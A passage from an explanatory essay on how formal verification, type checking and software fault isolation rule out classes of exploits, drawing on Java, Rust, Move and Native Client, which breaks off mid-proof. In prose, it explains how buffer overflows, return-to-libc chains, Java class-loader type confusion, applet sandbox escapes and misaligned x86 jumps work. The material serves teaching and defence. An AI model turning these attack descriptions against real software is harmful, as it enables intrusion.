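# Formal verification as a way to rule out classes of software exploit, and how far it reaches for AI systems

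## What it means to rule out an exploit by proof

Formal verification is the practice of proving mathematically that every possible run of a program satisfies a stated property. Engineers have applied it to compilers, operating-system kernels and cryptographic code. In computer security its target is the exploit: an input or program that makes a system do something its designers meant to exclude. Most security work goes another way. Someone finds a flaw, the vendor patches it, and the search starts over. Whether that cycle can ever end depends on whether every system has some exploit, or whether a proof can exclude whole classes of them at once. (A more speculative version of the question concerns minds, and whether for each mind there is some idea that would take it over.)

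Chong, Guttman and colleagues write in *Report on the NSF Workshop on Formal Methods for Security* (2016) that proofs about computer systems can rule out entire classes of attack, including attacks nobody has thought of yet, as long as the real system matches the assumptions of the mathematical model. This condition is as important as the guarantee, and both depend on what counts as an exploit.

### An exploit is a program

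Suppose a function reads a name into a buffer, a stretch of memory with room for 64 characters. The memory near the buffer holds the return address, which is the location of the instruction to resume when the function finishes. The function copies the name with a loop that runs until the input ends, without checking whether the buffer is full. A 200-character name therefore overflows the buffer and replaces the return address with the characters at that point in the name. If an attacker chose those characters to spell the buffer's address and filled the buffer with machine instructions, the processor jumps to the buffer when the function finishes and executes those instructions.

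This is a buffer overflow. *Exploit Programming* (Bratus, Locasto and colleagues, 2011) points out that the victim's own code does both the copying and the jump, through its copying loop and its return instruction. In 1997 the hacker Solar Designer showed that the attacker need not supply any instructions, because the standard library loaded with the program already contains code that opens a command shell. The overlong input only has to plant that code's address and arguments. Others then chained such snippets together, until the input was in effect a program, written in an instruction set that nobody had designed. Hackers call the thing that executes it a "weird machine".

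Dullien's *Weird machines, exploitability, and provable unexploitability* formally defines ideas about exploits that had been folklore. A programmer has in mind an intended machine, with certain states and transitions between them, and writes a program to emulate it on a general-purpose computer. Some configurations of the computer's memory represent states of the intended machine, and some occur briefly during the transitions between those states. All other configurations are weird states. If a bug or a hardware fault puts the computer into a weird state, the program keeps applying its usual transitions, now to meaningless data, and each further input selects the next transition. The resulting accidental computer is called the weird machine, and an exploit is a program for it that breaks a security property of the intended machine.

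On this account, a defence that blocks one style of attack leaves the attacker with others, and Dullien thinks most such defences will fail for that reason. Given enough preparation time, non-exploitability is "the exception, not the rule". But Dullien also proves that there are exceptions. The test case is a small server that stores up to 5,000 pairs of a 32-bit password and a 32-bit secret, and returns a secret to anyone who sends its password. An attacker who sends n messages should obtain someone else's secret with probability at most n/2³², which is no better than guessing. Dullien then lets the attacker flip any single bit of memory outside the processor's registers, once, at any moment.

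One version of the server keeps its pairs in a linked list, where each record holds the address of the next. An attacker can break this version with a single bit flip, which shifts one of those addresses by one cell so that the server reads a "record" that straddles two real ones. When the server deletes this false record, it overwrites the victim's password with a number the attacker can predict, and the attacker sends that number to get the secret. The other version keeps its pairs in a plain table and searches it from end to end. A flip there can do only a few things, such as change one bit of a stored password. An attacker who can't flip bits can match the output of any attack that uses one flip by sending at most 10,000 extra messages, which barely help in guessing a password from four billion possibilities.

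So the claim that every system has an exploit is false, at least for a toy program and a stated attacker. The safe server does the same job as the other one, but it is cruder and slower.

### Proof and testing

Bratus and colleagues remark that an exploit is itself a proof. It shows by example that a program can run in a way people believed impossible. Verification has to prove that no such run exists, which examples cannot do.

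A one-line function shows how proof differs from testing. The function uses a 32-bit whole number h to choose one of ten slots in a table, numbered 0 to 9. It takes the absolute value of h, divides by 10 and returns the remainder. The specification, the precise statement of what the program must do or must never do, is that the result lies between 0 and 9 for every h. A million random tests will almost certainly pass, but an attempt to prove the specification fails. If h is zero or positive, the absolute value is h and the remainder is in range. If h is negative, the absolute value should be −h, but 32-bit numbers run from −2,147,483,648 to 2,147,483,647, so the lowest number has no positive counterpart. In Java and similar languages, negating it gives the same negative number back, so the remainder is −8 and the function points eight places before the start of the table.

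Only one input in 4.3 billion fails, but an attacker needs only one. Taking the remainder before the absolute value fixes the problem, because the remainder is always between −9 and 9. A two-line argument then covers every input. A modern machine could also test all 4.3 billion values given enough time, but two such inputs have about 1.8 × 10¹⁹ combinations, which is too many to test.

"Never points outside the table" is a safety property. Alpern and Schneider (1985), in *Defining Liveness*, give the exact definition. Treat a run σ as an infinite sequence of states (a run that ends repeats its last state for ever) and a property P as a set of runs. P is a safety property if, for every run σ that is not in P, there is a step i such that no continuation of the first i states is in P:

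σ ∉ P ⇒ ∃i ∀β: σ[..i]β ∉ P

Every violation of a safety property happens at an identifiable moment, and nothing afterwards can undo it. By contrast, no finite part of a run can violate "the program eventually halts", because a program that is still running may yet stop. Alpern and Schneider class that as a liveness property, and they prove that every property of single runs is the intersection of a safety property and a liveness property.

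### What a proof rests on

Proofs can also contain errors. Dullien's argument for the table-based server depends on two lemmas that the paper leaves to the reader as easy to verify from the code. They probably are, but security experts have often been wrong about what was obvious. The usual remedy is a proof checker, a small program that accepts a proof only if every step follows from fixed rules. Chlipala (2018), in *The Surprising Security Benefits of End-to-End Formal Proofs*, points out that one checker can serve for machine code, Java programs, network protocols and access rules, so people need to trust one small program instead of a new and complicated security tool for each job.

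Any checker used for this must be sound, meaning that every program it accepts has the property being checked. A sound checker may still reject some programs that have the property.

Even a sound checker leaves a trusted base, which is everything that must be correct for the guarantee to hold, including the checker itself, the hardware and the mathematical model of the machine. Dullien lists hardware faults among the sources of weird states. The known example is Rowhammer, in which a program reads certain memory cells so rapidly that bits flip in neighbouring ones. A proof based on a model in which memory keeps its contents gives no protection against this. More generally, Chong and colleagues say that formal methods can exclude only those gaps that the model can express.

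The specification may also be wrong, and a proof checker cannot detect the error. Chlipala responds with the example of a program meant to find the shortest path through a network. One could prove that it returns a shortest path, or merely some path, or merely a list of points in the network. A buffer overflow would make all three theorems false, because an attacker could use it to make the program return anything. So proving almost any modest theorem about a program's results rules out the most common attacks, without anyone having to list them.

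That is right for bugs that give an attacker control, but much weaker for leaks. Chlipala's own counterexample is Spectre and Meltdown, two attacks made public in 2018, in which a processor's speculative work leaves traces in its caches that reveal secrets through timing. The shortest-path theorem remains true even when a secret leaks this way. Chlipala proposes including time in the model and proving the software and processor correct together. Joining the two proofs also shrinks the trusted base, because the final theorem is stated only in terms of the bytes going in and out. The formal version of the processor's instruction manual becomes an internal detail, and any serious mistake in it will make a proof fail.

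### The halting problem and Rice's theorem

A well-known result gives reason to think that this kind of proof must fail in general. In 1936 Alan Turing proved that no algorithm can correctly decide, for every program and input, whether the program halts on that input. If such an algorithm existed, we could use it to write a new program that takes a program's text, checks whether that program halts when given its own text, and then does the opposite. Given its own text, the new program would halt if and only if it did not halt, which is a contradiction.

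Henry Gordon Rice extended the result in 1953. Rice's theorem is that, for any non-trivial property of the function a program computes, no algorithm can decide for every program whether it has that property. A property is non-trivial if at least one program has it and at least one lacks it. Such a property depends only on the function, so two programs with the same outputs for the same inputs either both have it or both lack it.

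The proof uses the halting problem. Suppose a program that loops forever lacks the property (if it has the property, the same argument works for the opposite property), and let F be a program that has the property. For any program D and input x, we can build a new program that runs D on x, ignores the result, and then behaves like F. This new program has the property if and only if D halts on x, so an algorithm that decided the property would solve the halting problem.

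Security properties often concern a program's steps rather than its outputs, but the same construction applies to them. In *Computability Classes for Enforcement Mechanisms*, Hamlen, Morrisett and Schneider use the example of a program that must never write to cells 0 to 511, which represent a disk's boot sector, the part a computer starts up from. A program can run an arbitrary second program with its memory shifted above cell 511, then write to cell 0 if the second program ends. Deciding whether the boot sector is ever overwritten then requires solving the halting problem. A real computer has finite memory, which makes the question decidable in principle. This helps little in practice, because even Dullien's toy computer, with 65,536 cells of 32 bits each, has 2 to the power of 2,097,152 possible memory contents.

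The theorem rules out a single procedure that gives the right answer about every program, but it still allows proofs about particular programs. The people who build a system also have considerable control over which programs they have to verify. They can get around the theorem in four ways, each with its own drawback.

A checker can reject some harmless programs. Suppose it accepts a program only if every write instruction names a fixed address of 512 or above. A computer can verify that by reading the program's text once, and no accepted program can write to the boot sector. The checker also rejects a program that computes its address as 300 + 300, and one whose only bad write is in a branch that never executes. Hamlen and colleagues show that checks made before a program runs can enforce exactly the decidable properties, so we need a decidable property that implies the one we want without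 rejecting too many harmless programs.

Designers can also restrict the programming language. If the only loop available is "repeat n times", with n fixed before the loop begins, and functions cannot call themselves, then every program halts and nobody has to check that it does. (The same idea works for the language of a program's inputs.) Programmers then can't write some computations, including an interpreter for the language itself. The restriction guarantees only halting, and whether such a program returns zero on every input is still undecidable.

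Alternatively, the checker can require the program's author to supply a proof, since checking a proof is far easier than finding one. Consider a loop that starts with i = 512, writes to cell i, adds 2, and stops when i equals exactly 1,000. The author claims that at the start of every pass, i is even and lies between 512 and 1,000. The checker confirms that the claim holds at the start, that each pass preserves it (if i is not yet 1,000, it is at most 998, so adding 2 keeps it in range and even), and that it implies no write lands below cell 512. The author has to supply the fact that i is even, because without it the claim would allow i to be 999. The next step would then skip from 999 to 1,001 and the loop would keep going. On a machine whose numbers wrap around, i would eventually reach 1, and the loop would write inside the boot sector.

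The last way is to watch the program as it runs and stop it just before it does harm. In *Enforceable Security Policies*, Schneider gives the example of a rule that a program may not send messages after reading a file. The monitor needs one bit of memory to record whether the program has read a file. Once it has, the monitor ends the run at any attempt to send. It never has to look further ahead than the next step. But the bug stays in the program, and the monitor prevents a breach by causing a crash, which may be no better in a device such as a pacemaker. Schneider also proves that monitors of this kind can enforce only safety properties, because they have access only to what has already happened in a single run. Hamlen and colleagues later showed that no real monitor can enforce some of the properties that Schneider's conditions allowed.

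### Memory, processor time and communication

Most of the harm a program can do to its surroundings comes through the memory it accesses, the processor time it uses and the messages it sends. Ruling out these harms requires proving different kinds of property.

Memory access is the easy case. The requirement that a program never read or write outside its own region is a safety property, because it applies to each run separately and any violation happens at a specific instruction. All four methods apply to it.

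Whether a requirement on processor time is a safety property depends on its wording. "Finishes eventually" applies to single runs, but it is a liveness property, so a monitor could wait forever without seeing a violation that would justify stopping the program. Engineers replace it with the stricter requirement "finishes within a million steps", which is a safety property. Other requirements on time apply to many runs together. *Hyperproperties* (Clarkson and Schneider, 2009) gives the example of keeping the mean response time over all runs below one second. Whether a slow run is acceptable then depends on how fast the others are.

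Rules about what a program communicates need both kinds of property. Sending data only through a channel that someone inspects is a safety property of single runs, but revealing nothing about a secret is a property of the program's whole set of runs. If a program prints 7, we can't tell from that run alone whether the output reveals anything, because the answer depends on what the program would have printed had the secret been different. Clarkson and Schneider call requirements on the whole set of runs hyperproperties. The best-known is noninterference, which requires that changing the secret inputs never changes what an outside observer sees.

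Removing some of a program's possible runs can never break a safety property, but it can break some hyperproperties. Clarkson and Schneider describe a system that chooses freely between printing 0, printing 1 and printing a secret bit. The possible outputs are 0 and 1 whatever the secret is, so the set of outputs reveals nothing about it. A programmer turning this loose design into working code might remove some of the freedom and make the system always print the secret bit. Every remaining run was allowed by the original design, but the output now reveals the secret.

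Schneider notes that no monitor can enforce secrecy exactly, so monitors meant to prevent leaks enforce a stricter rule that implies secrecy. The rule against sending after reading a file is one example. It will stop a weather program that reads its settings and then requests the forecast, even though no secret is at risk.

The three resources are not fully separate either. A program that takes longer when a password begins with the right letter leaks information about the password through its use of processor time, even if it never writes outside its region or opens a connection. *Formalization of Security* (Barthe, 2026), a survey of machine-checked security proofs, describes the corresponding requirement that a program's resource use must not depend on secrets. A step limit can't enforce this requirement, because the requirement compares runs with different secrets, and every one of those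 runs may be well within the limit.

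## Type-checked languages: Java and Rust

Most programmers who rely on proofs about memory access never write one. They use a type checker, which works out what kind of value each expression in a program produces and rejects the program if the kinds don't fit together. If a language's designers prove once that accepted programs never misuse memory, the proof covers every program the checker later accepts.

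### How a type checker yields a theorem

Take a toy language whose values are whole numbers, the booleans true and false, and references, which are addresses of memory cells. The checker has six rules, in which Ref T is the type of a reference to a cell holding a value of type T:

- A number has type Num, and true and false have type Bool.
- e₁ + e₂ has type Num if e₁ and e₂ both have type Num.
- "if e₁ then e₂ else e₃" has type T if e₁ has type Bool and e₂ and e₃ both have type T.
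- "new e", which creates a cell containing the value of e, has type Ref T if e has type T.
- "!e", which reads a cell, has type T if e has type Ref T.
- "e₁ := e₂", which overwrites a cell and returns the value written, has type T if e₁ has type Ref T and e₂ has type T.

No rule gives a type to !5, so the checker rejects it. An ordinary processor would read whatever is at address 5. In the toy language's formal definition, !5 is stuck, meaning it isn't a finished value and no execution step applies to it. The theorem to prove is that a program with a type never gets stuck.

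The standard proof uses two lemmas about a program partway through its run. Let μ be the contents of memory, and let Σ list every cell created so far and the type of its contents. The list Σ exists only in the proof. We say μ matches Σ if both have the same cells and each cell holds a value of the listed type. An address ℓ has type Ref Σ(ℓ) if ℓ is in Σ, and otherwise it has no type.

Progress: if e has type T and μ matches Σ, then e is a finished value or can take a step.

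Preservation means that if e has type T, μ matches Σ, and one step turns e and μ into e′ and μ′, then there is a Σ′ extending Σ such that e′ has type T and μ′ matches Σ′.

Progress means that a well-typed program can take another step unless it has finished, and preservation means that it is still well-typed after that step. A well-typed program therefore never reaches a stuck state.

The proofs of both lemmas take the rules one at a time. If !e has type T and e is fully evaluated, then e is a value of type Ref T, so it must be an address in Σ. Since μ matches Σ, the cell at that address exists and holds a value of type T, so the read succeeds and its result has the right type. A write replaces a value with another of the same type, so memory still matches Σ. "New" picks an unused address and adds it to Σ.

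This is also why a program can't forge a pointer. A programmer can't type in an address because the language has no notation for one, and can't compute one by addition because addition produces only numbers. By preservation, every address in a running program is in Σ, and only "new" adds addresses to Σ.

Like the checker for boot-sector writes, this one rejects some harmless programs, such as "if true then 5 else false". The theorem sets no limit on processor time. If we add loops to the language, a program that loops forever still satisfies progress because it can always take another step, so we need a separate limit on processor time to stop it.

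The toy language also never frees memory. If we add an instruction to free a cell, preservation fails, because a program can keep a copy of the cell's address. Σ then lists a cell that no longer exists, and if the runtime reuses the space for a value of another type, the program can read a number as an address. Java solves this with a garbage collector, which frees memory only when the program can no longer reach it, and Rust does so by restricting references.

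### The Java bytecode verifier

A Java compiler translates source text into bytecode, the instruction set of the Java virtual machine (JVM). In the 1990s, web browsers began to download and run small bytecode programs, called applets, from strangers' websites. Bytecode may not come from a trustworthy compiler, since an attacker can write it by hand, so the JVM checks it at load time. The alternative is to check types at every instruction as the program runs, which RWTH Aachen's *Static Program Analysis* (2011) describes as slow. Verified code doesn't need these extra checks and runs at full speed.

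Bytecode instructions keep their data in numbered registers and on a stack. For each instruction, the verifier records the type of every register and stack entry just before the instruction executes. It then simulates the instruction on types instead of values. Lecture slides from TU Munich illustrate this with a five-instruction loop. In the example, B is a subclass of A, so every B object is also an A object, and A objects have a field F of type A. At the start, the stack is empty, register 0 holds a B object, and register 1 holds an integer.

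| Instruction | Stack and registers, first pass | Stack and registers, final |
|---|---|---|
| 0: push register 0 | empty; B, integer | empty; B, integer |
| 1: pop into register 1 | B; B, integer | A; B, unusable |
| 2: push register 0 | empty; B, B | empty; B, A |
| 3: replace object with its field F | B; B, B | B; B, A |
| 4: jump to instruction 1 | A; B, B | A; B, A |

The jump gives instruction 1 a second set of types, which the verifier must merge with the first. The stack may hold a B or an A, so the verifier records their nearest common superclass, A. Register 1 may hold an integer or an object, which have no common superclass, so the verifier marks it unusable and would reject any instruction that read it there. The verifier then repeats the simulation from instruction 1 with the merged types. This time the jump adds no new types, and the verifier accepts the method. The process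 always ends because merging only moves types up a class hierarchy of finite height.

The next case in the slides omits instruction 1, so each pass through the loop leaves two more values on the stack. The jump reaches a point where the verifier had recorded an empty stack, but the stack now has two entries, so the verifier rejects the method.

The verifier also rejects code that does arithmetic on references, reads a register before anything has been stored there, uses an object before its constructor has run, or accesses another class's private fields. It can't check properties that depend on runtime values, such as whether an array index is in range, so the JVM checks those as the program runs. Newer compilers record in the bytecode file the types that hold where execution paths merge, so the verifier only has to confirm them. This is a small-scale version of supplying a proof with the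 code.

Leroy's *Java bytecode verification* surveys work in which researchers used proof assistants to specify the verifier and prove it correct. Those proofs concern mathematical models of the JVM. Checked code can still take over a real JVM if it differs from the model, and this has happened repeatedly in Java's history.

### Two holes in Java's types

In *Java is not type-safe*, Saraswat (1997) showed that code could treat an object of one class as an object of another. The weakness was in class loaders, which fetch a class's code when a program first needs it. Java programs can define their own loaders, and two loaders can load different classes with the same name.

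Saraswat's example has a class R with a private number r, set to 1, and a helper class that hands out R objects. The attacker writes a false R in which r is public, and a loader that takes the helper from the system but R from the attacker's folder. When the attacker's code gets an R from the helper, the object is genuine, but the JVM handles it according to the false definition. The program printed the private value and changed it to 300960. Saraswat then added extra fields to the false R, so that the JVM read r from beyond the end of the real object, and the program printed 6946913, the value in memory there. The JVM crashed when the program called a method that existed only in the false R.

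In the toy language's terms, Σ listed two different types under one name, so a check that compared only names could not keep memory matched to Σ. The fault was in the type system's design, which should have identified each type by its name and its loader. Saraswat thought that the HotJava browser's loaders probably kept applets from exploiting it. Liang and Bracha's *Dynamic Class Loading in the Java Virtual Machine* described how Sun, the company behind Java, would keep types safe with user-defined loaders. The JVM now records which loaders must resolve a name to the same class and refuses to link classes if they don't. The repair took more than one attempt. Coglio and Goldberg's *Type safety in the JVM* (2001) reported that class names could still be spoofed in a later version of Sun's verifier. They noticed the bugs while writing a formal specification of the verifier.

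A hole in the source language lasted longer. *Java and Scala's Type Systems are Unsound* (Amin and Tate, 2016) presents a short Java function that turns a value of any type T into any other type U without a cast (an explicit request to treat a value as another type). The function relies on generics, which allow types such as "list of strings". It declares a variable whose type makes sense only if T is a subtype of some type Z and Z is a subtype of U. The compiler therefore infers that T is a subtype of U and accepts the T value as a U.

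That reasoning is unsafe because the variable can hold null, Java's empty reference, which belongs to every reference type. If the variable had to contain a real object, the reasoning would be harmless, because no such object can exist when T and U are unrelated. The function stores null in the variable, and the test program uses this to turn the number 0 into a "string".

When Amin and Tate ran the program, the JVM stopped it with an error. The JVM has no generics, so the compiler erases them and inserts run-time casts where the erased types mattered. The cast from a number to a string failed. The compiler's type checker is therefore outside the trusted base for memory safety, and its mistake caused only a crash, though Amin and Tate leave open whether it could cause harm indirectly.

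The hole had existed since 2004, although researchers had formalised Java many times. They usually proved soundness for a small language containing the feature they were studying, but this problem arises only when a language has both generics and null. A correct proof about part of a language gives little assurance about how that part interacts with the rest.

### The Java sandbox and its libraries

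Memory safety doesn't stop a program from deleting files, since a well-typed applet can call the library method that deletes them. Java restricted such calls with the Security Manager, a component that library methods checked with before they accessed files, the network or other resources. *JEP 411* (2021), a proposal from OpenJDK, the project that develops Java, describes the Security Manager as a separate layer from the memory safety of the language and the JVM.

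When code tried to open a file, the Security Manager checked the permissions of all the code in the chain of calls that led there, and blocked access if an untrusted applet was anywhere in the chain. This rule would also block some harmless requests. For instance, when a program gets the local time, the library reads a time zone file that the program itself may not have permission to read. Library methods could therefore assert their own permissions and have the check ignore their callers.

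*JEP 486* (Mullan and Buckley, 2024) reports that over 1,000 Java library methods had to check permissions and over 1,200 had to raise their own privileges. Code could escape the sandbox if a single check was missing, or if a method raised its privileges and then did something its caller had chosen.

Attackers found many such mistakes in 2012 and 2013, when malicious web pages repeatedly used applets to break into visitors' computers. In a typical attack, the applet passed the verifier, reached internal classes by using the library to look up methods by name, and got trusted code to switch off the Security Manager. Such an attack need not violate the type rules. Other attacks broke type safety by exploiting faults in the JVM or in library code that wrote to memory without the usual checks.

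The claim that checked Java code can't take over its virtual machine is false of the JVMs people used. Its supporters can fairly reply that the verifier did most of what it was designed to do. Changing one rule about names and loaders repairs a fault in the type theory for all programs at once. There was no comparable fix for the libraries, where the trusted base included thousands of methods and grew with each release. OpenJDK says that putting checks everywhere was feasible in Java 1.0 because it had only eight core packages. It also notes that a series of individually safe operations could together do something that should have required a stronger permission.

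OpenJDK deprecated the Security Manager in Java 17, in 2021, and disabled it permanently in Java 24, in March 2025. The escapes were not the main stated reason. Browsers had stopped running applets, few other programs used the Security Manager, and every new library feature had to take it into account. Mullan and Buckley advise people to confine the whole Java runtime from outside instead, with containers or operating-system mechanisms. (Capabilities, which attach the right to use a resource to an unforgeable reference, would be another way to control access within a language.)

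### Rust: ownership, borrowing and unsafe code

Rust is a language for operating systems and similar software, where programmers want to control memory without a garbage collector. Each value has one owner, usually a variable, and the compiler inserts code to free the value when its owner goes out of scope. Assigning the value to another variable moves ownership, and the compiler rejects any later use of the old variable.

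Code can also borrow a value through a reference. The compiler's borrow checker enforces two rules. A reference must not outlive the value it points to, and while a reference that allows changes is in use, no other reference to the same data may be in use. Suppose a program takes a reference to the first element of a growable list and then appends to the list. Appending may move the list to a larger block of memory and free the old one, leaving the reference pointing at freed memory. Appending borrows the list for changes, so the compiler rejects the program if it uses the old reference afterwards. The second rule also prevents data races, in which one thread changes data while another is using it.

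Some necessary code can't follow these rules, including code that controls hardware and the code inside the growable list itself. Rust lets programmers put such code in blocks marked "unsafe", where they may follow raw addresses and call functions written in C. The compiler still performs most of its checks there, but the programmer is responsible for the rest. (Confining the C code itself requires something like WebAssembly, a sandboxed instruction set.)

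Unsafe blocks rule out a plain proof by progress and preservation, because the type rules don't cover what happens inside them. RustBelt, a machine-checked proof published by Ralf Jung and colleagues in 2018, instead treats each type as a condition on memory and on who may use it. A library that contains unsafe code counts as safe if its functions maintain the conditions given by their types, whatever safe code calls them. The main theorem is that well-typed safe code combined with such libraries never misuses memory. Jung and colleagues proved that several important standard libraries meet this requirement, including those for locks and shared ownership, but each new library that contains unsafe code needs its own proof.

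RustBelt covers a simplified core of Rust, not the compiler. *How Could Formal Verification Help with Cyber Resilience?* makes the same distinction between Rust's verified rules and its unverified implementation. Part of the gap is that the Rust Project's own formal model of the language is incomplete. The project's *Borrow checking in a-mir-formality* proposes adding key parts of borrow checking to it.

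Even so, the results in practice are good. Vander Stoep (2025), in *Rust in Android*, reports that memory-safety bugs fell below 20% of Android's vulnerabilities for the first time in 2025, compared with an industry norm of around 70%. The number of these bugs has also fallen, so the lower share is not just the result of other bugs becoming more common. Google had earlier reported a decline from 223 memory-safety vulnerabilities in 2019 to fewer than 50 in 2024, according to The Hacker News (2025).

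Vander Stoep also compares the rates of memory-safety vulnerabilities in the two groups of languages. Google had found one potential vulnerability in Android's roughly 5 million lines of Rust, or 0.2 per million lines, compared with a historical figure of about 1,000 per million for Android's C and C++. One bug is too few for a reliable estimate, and people have had much longer to find bugs in the older code. But even if another 99 bugs were undiscovered, the Rust figure would be 20 per million lines, a fiftieth of the figure for C and C++.

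The one bug was a buffer overflow in unsafe code in CrabbyAVIF, an image library. Google caught it before release, and Android's memory allocator would have blocked an exploit because it surrounds large blocks of memory with pages that crash the program if touched. About 4% of Android's Rust code is in unsafe blocks. In the wider Rust ecosystem, unsafe code accounts for about two thirds of vulnerabilities, according to a presentation by the developers of Lean, a programming language with a built-in proof checker. They describe a Google team building tools that let programmers state and prove the conditions unsafe Rust code relies on, which now usually appear only in comments.

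### A machine-checked borrow checker for Move

Move is a language for smart contracts, programs that hold and transfer money on a blockchain. Like the JVM, the Sui and Aptos blockchains check its bytecode before running it, partly with a borrow checker. An error in the borrow checker could let an attacker steal funds by using a dangling reference, one whose target no longer exists. *Tracking Borrows with Regular Expressions* (Nowacki, Blackshear and colleagues, 2026) presents a new borrow checker for Move, with a proof in Lean that its rules are sound.

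Move is easier to verify than Rust because its data structures can't contain references. Every reference points to a local variable or to something that the program can reach from a variable by following named fields. For each pair of references ρ and ρ′, the checker keeps a regular expression, a pattern describing every sequence of fields that might lead from ρ to ρ′. Before a write through ρ, it requires:

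∀ρ′: L(paths(ρ, ρ′)) ⊆ {ε}

Here L is the set of sequences that match the pattern and ε is the empty sequence. The condition means that no reference in use may point inside the value that the program is about to overwrite. Suppose a value can take two forms, one with a field x and the other with fields x and y. If a program held a reference to y and then switched the value to the form without y, the reference would be left dangling, so the checker rejects the program.

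The checker allows a second reference to the whole value, which Rust would forbid. This is safe because Move programs run in a single thread and the new value has the same type as the old one, so the second reference still points to something valid. The toy language's write rule is safe for the same reason. Where two branches meet, the checker merges the patterns by allowing the sequences from either branch, much as the Java verifier moves up to a common superclass.

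The theorem applies to a function that passes the checker, calls only functions that respect their declared types, and starts from a well-formed state. Such a function never reaches a preventable error, however many steps it runs. Preventable errors include following a dangling reference, using a variable after its value has moved, and confusing types. Division by zero, a deliberate abort and running out of steps count as acceptable, so this proof doesn't limit processor time either.

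The proof uses progress and preservation, and nearly all the difficulty is in preservation. The toy language needed only the condition "μ matches Σ", but Move needed a condition with 35 clauses, and the proof had to re-establish all of them in each of 41 cases. The proof is about 39,000 lines of Lean. One researcher, Ilya Sergey, produced it in 27 working days by directing Anthropic's Claude models, which wrote most of it. Nowacki and colleagues think such a project would traditionally take a person-year, while Lean's developers estimate five to six months.

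Failed proof attempts exposed three mistakes that testing and code review had missed. Two were slips in writing down the rules, and the third was a design flaw. The design checked too many references when a function returned, so it rejected some valid programs. The Move team confirmed and fixed the flaw.

The proof is about a model of Move written in Lean. To test whether the model matches the production system, Nowacki and colleagues ran the Lean version of the checker on 156 programs from the Move compiler's test suite and got the same verdicts. They tested the model of execution on only 31 programs, comparing final outcomes but not intermediate steps. The model omits some features, including generics and the blockchain's permanent storage.

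The proof doesn't cover the version meant for the Sui blockchain, which is separate code. Nowacki and colleagues ran that version on all 292,141 packages published on Sui, and it accepted every package that the existing checker accepts. The new checker therefore won't break existing contracts, but this test can't establish that it rejects every dangerous contract. When they wrote, Sui had not yet put the new checker into production.

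## Confining machine code to its own memory

Type checking helps only with programs written in a checked language, and much software is in C or C++, where a program can compute any number and use it as an address. The usual way to run such code without trusting its author is to give it its own process, because the processor prevents each process from accessing the others' memory. But switching between processes is slow, so a database that calls an untrusted function a million times in one query needs a faster method.

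### Address masking

*Efficient Software-Based Fault Isolation* (Wahbe, Lucco and colleagues, 1993) describes software fault isolation, which runs an untrusted program in the same process as its host and adds instructions to the program to keep it out of the host's memory. The program gets one segment of memory for its code and another for its data, and all addresses in a segment begin with the same digits.

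Suppose addresses have eight hexadecimal digits, the first four identify the segment, and the program's data segment is 0042. The program may then write anywhere from 0042 0000 to 0042 FFFF. If it tries to store a number at 0017 7F10, which belongs to the host, two inserted instructions change the address just before the store:

- The first clears the segment digits, which turns 0017 7F10 into 0000 7F10.
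- The second fills in the program's own segment, which gives 0042 7F10.

The resulting address is 0042 7F10. Masking leaves an address already in segment 0042 unchanged, so a correct program behaves as before. Masking redirects bad addresses without detecting them, so a faulty program may overwrite its own data.

A program could bypass the mask by loading a register with an address in the host's memory and jumping straight to the store instruction. Wahbe and colleagues therefore reserve a register for masked addresses, make every masked store use it, and let only the inserted instructions change it. Wherever the program jumps within its own code, that register holds an address in the data segment by the time a store uses it.

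Jumps out of the code segment are also dangerous. The program could jump into the middle of one of the host's functions, or into its own data segment, where it may have written instructions without masks. So the inserted code masks jump targets too, using the code segment's digits. The program can't alter its code segment, because every store goes to the data segment. It can leave the code segment only through a table of fixed jumps to entry points that the host has approved.

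On a set of C programs, masking stores and jumps added about 4% to the running time on average. Masking reads as well, which is necessary if the host's memory contains secrets, raised this to 22% on one of the two test machines and 18% on the other. But a call between host and program took only about 1 microsecond, while a round trip between two processes took about 200. In a database query with 1.4 million calls to untrusted code, isolating that code this way added 5.7% to the running time, compared with an estimated 32% for separate processes.

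### Checking the finished code

Wahbe and colleagues modified a C compiler to insert the masks, but the host can't verify which compiler produced the code it receives. They therefore wrote a checker that examines the machine code when the host loads it. For each instruction that changes a reserved register, the checker confirms that the register holds a properly masked address before anything can use it. If an attacker's compiler leaves out a mask, the checker rejects the program. The compiler can be large and faulty without weakening the confinement, because only the much smaller checker is in the trusted base.

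Writing that checker is harder for x86 processors, which most desktop computers use, because their instructions vary in length. The five bytes B8 CD 80 00 00 are a harmless instruction that puts a number in a register. If a program jumps to the second byte, the processor instead reads CD 80, which on Linux is a request to the operating system. A checker that reads the code once from the beginning misses that request.

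Native Client, which Google built into Chrome to run machine code from websites, dealt with this by restricting where jumps can land. Every 32nd byte had to be the start of an instruction, and the program had to round any computed jump target to a multiple of 32. The rounding instruction and its jump had to be in the same 32-byte block, so that no computed jump could land between them. Google's checker for these rules had about 600 statements, and entrants in a public contest found exploitable bugs in early versions.

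*RockSalt* (Morrisett, Tan and colleagues, 2012) replaced the earlier checker with one of about 80 lines, written and proved correct in the proof assistant Coq. The new checker relies mainly on tables for recognising permitted instructions, which the team generated from a formal description of x86. The proof defines a safe state as one where the code is unchanged, the processor's segment settings are intact, and the next instruction is one the checker recognised. It then shows that an accepted program in a safe state always reaches another safe state within two steps. The program needs two steps when it rounds a jump target and then jumps. This result serves the same purpose as preservation in a type system.

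RockSalt was also faster than Google's checker, taking 0.24 seconds instead of 0.90 to check a program compiled from 200,000 lines of C. But Morrisett and colleagues translated it into C by hand to fit it into Native Client, and the proof doesn't cover the translation. They tested the C version on over two thousand generated programs, and it always agreed with Google's checker.

The formal description of x86 is also part of the trusted base. Morrisett and colleagues compared it with real processors on more than 10 million instruction executions, but these tests missed a flipped bit in a rare form of one instruction. They found the error when they failed to prove that no byte sequence has two meanings. Later, uwplse's *SaltShaker*, a tool that compares RockSalt's description with an independent one, found seven more bugs in it. Such a bug doesn't necessarily open a hole in the sandbox, but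 it means that part of the description the theorem relies on doesn't match real processors.

### The LFI proof

Lightweight Fault Isolation (LFI) is a recent system for ARM64, the processor design in most phones. Earlier versions of its checker were unsound because some permitted instructions changed registers in ways its developers hadn't expected. *Automated Formal Verification of a Software Fault Isolation System* (Sotoudeh and Yedidia, 2025) proves that programs accepted by the current checker never read or write outside their sandbox.

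Each sandbox is 4 GiB, or 2³² bytes, and starts at a multiple of that size. Register x21 always holds the sandbox's starting address, and ordinary reads and writes must take their address from register x18. A program can change x18 only with an instruction that combines the upper half of x21 with the lower half of another register. This instruction replaces the two masking instructions used in 1993.

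What makes the proof manageable is that LFI's checker has no memory. It looks at each instruction separately and accepts the program if every instruction is on a list L of permitted ones, in any order. The proof can therefore take instructions one at a time too. For an invariant I, which is a condition on the registers, it establishes:

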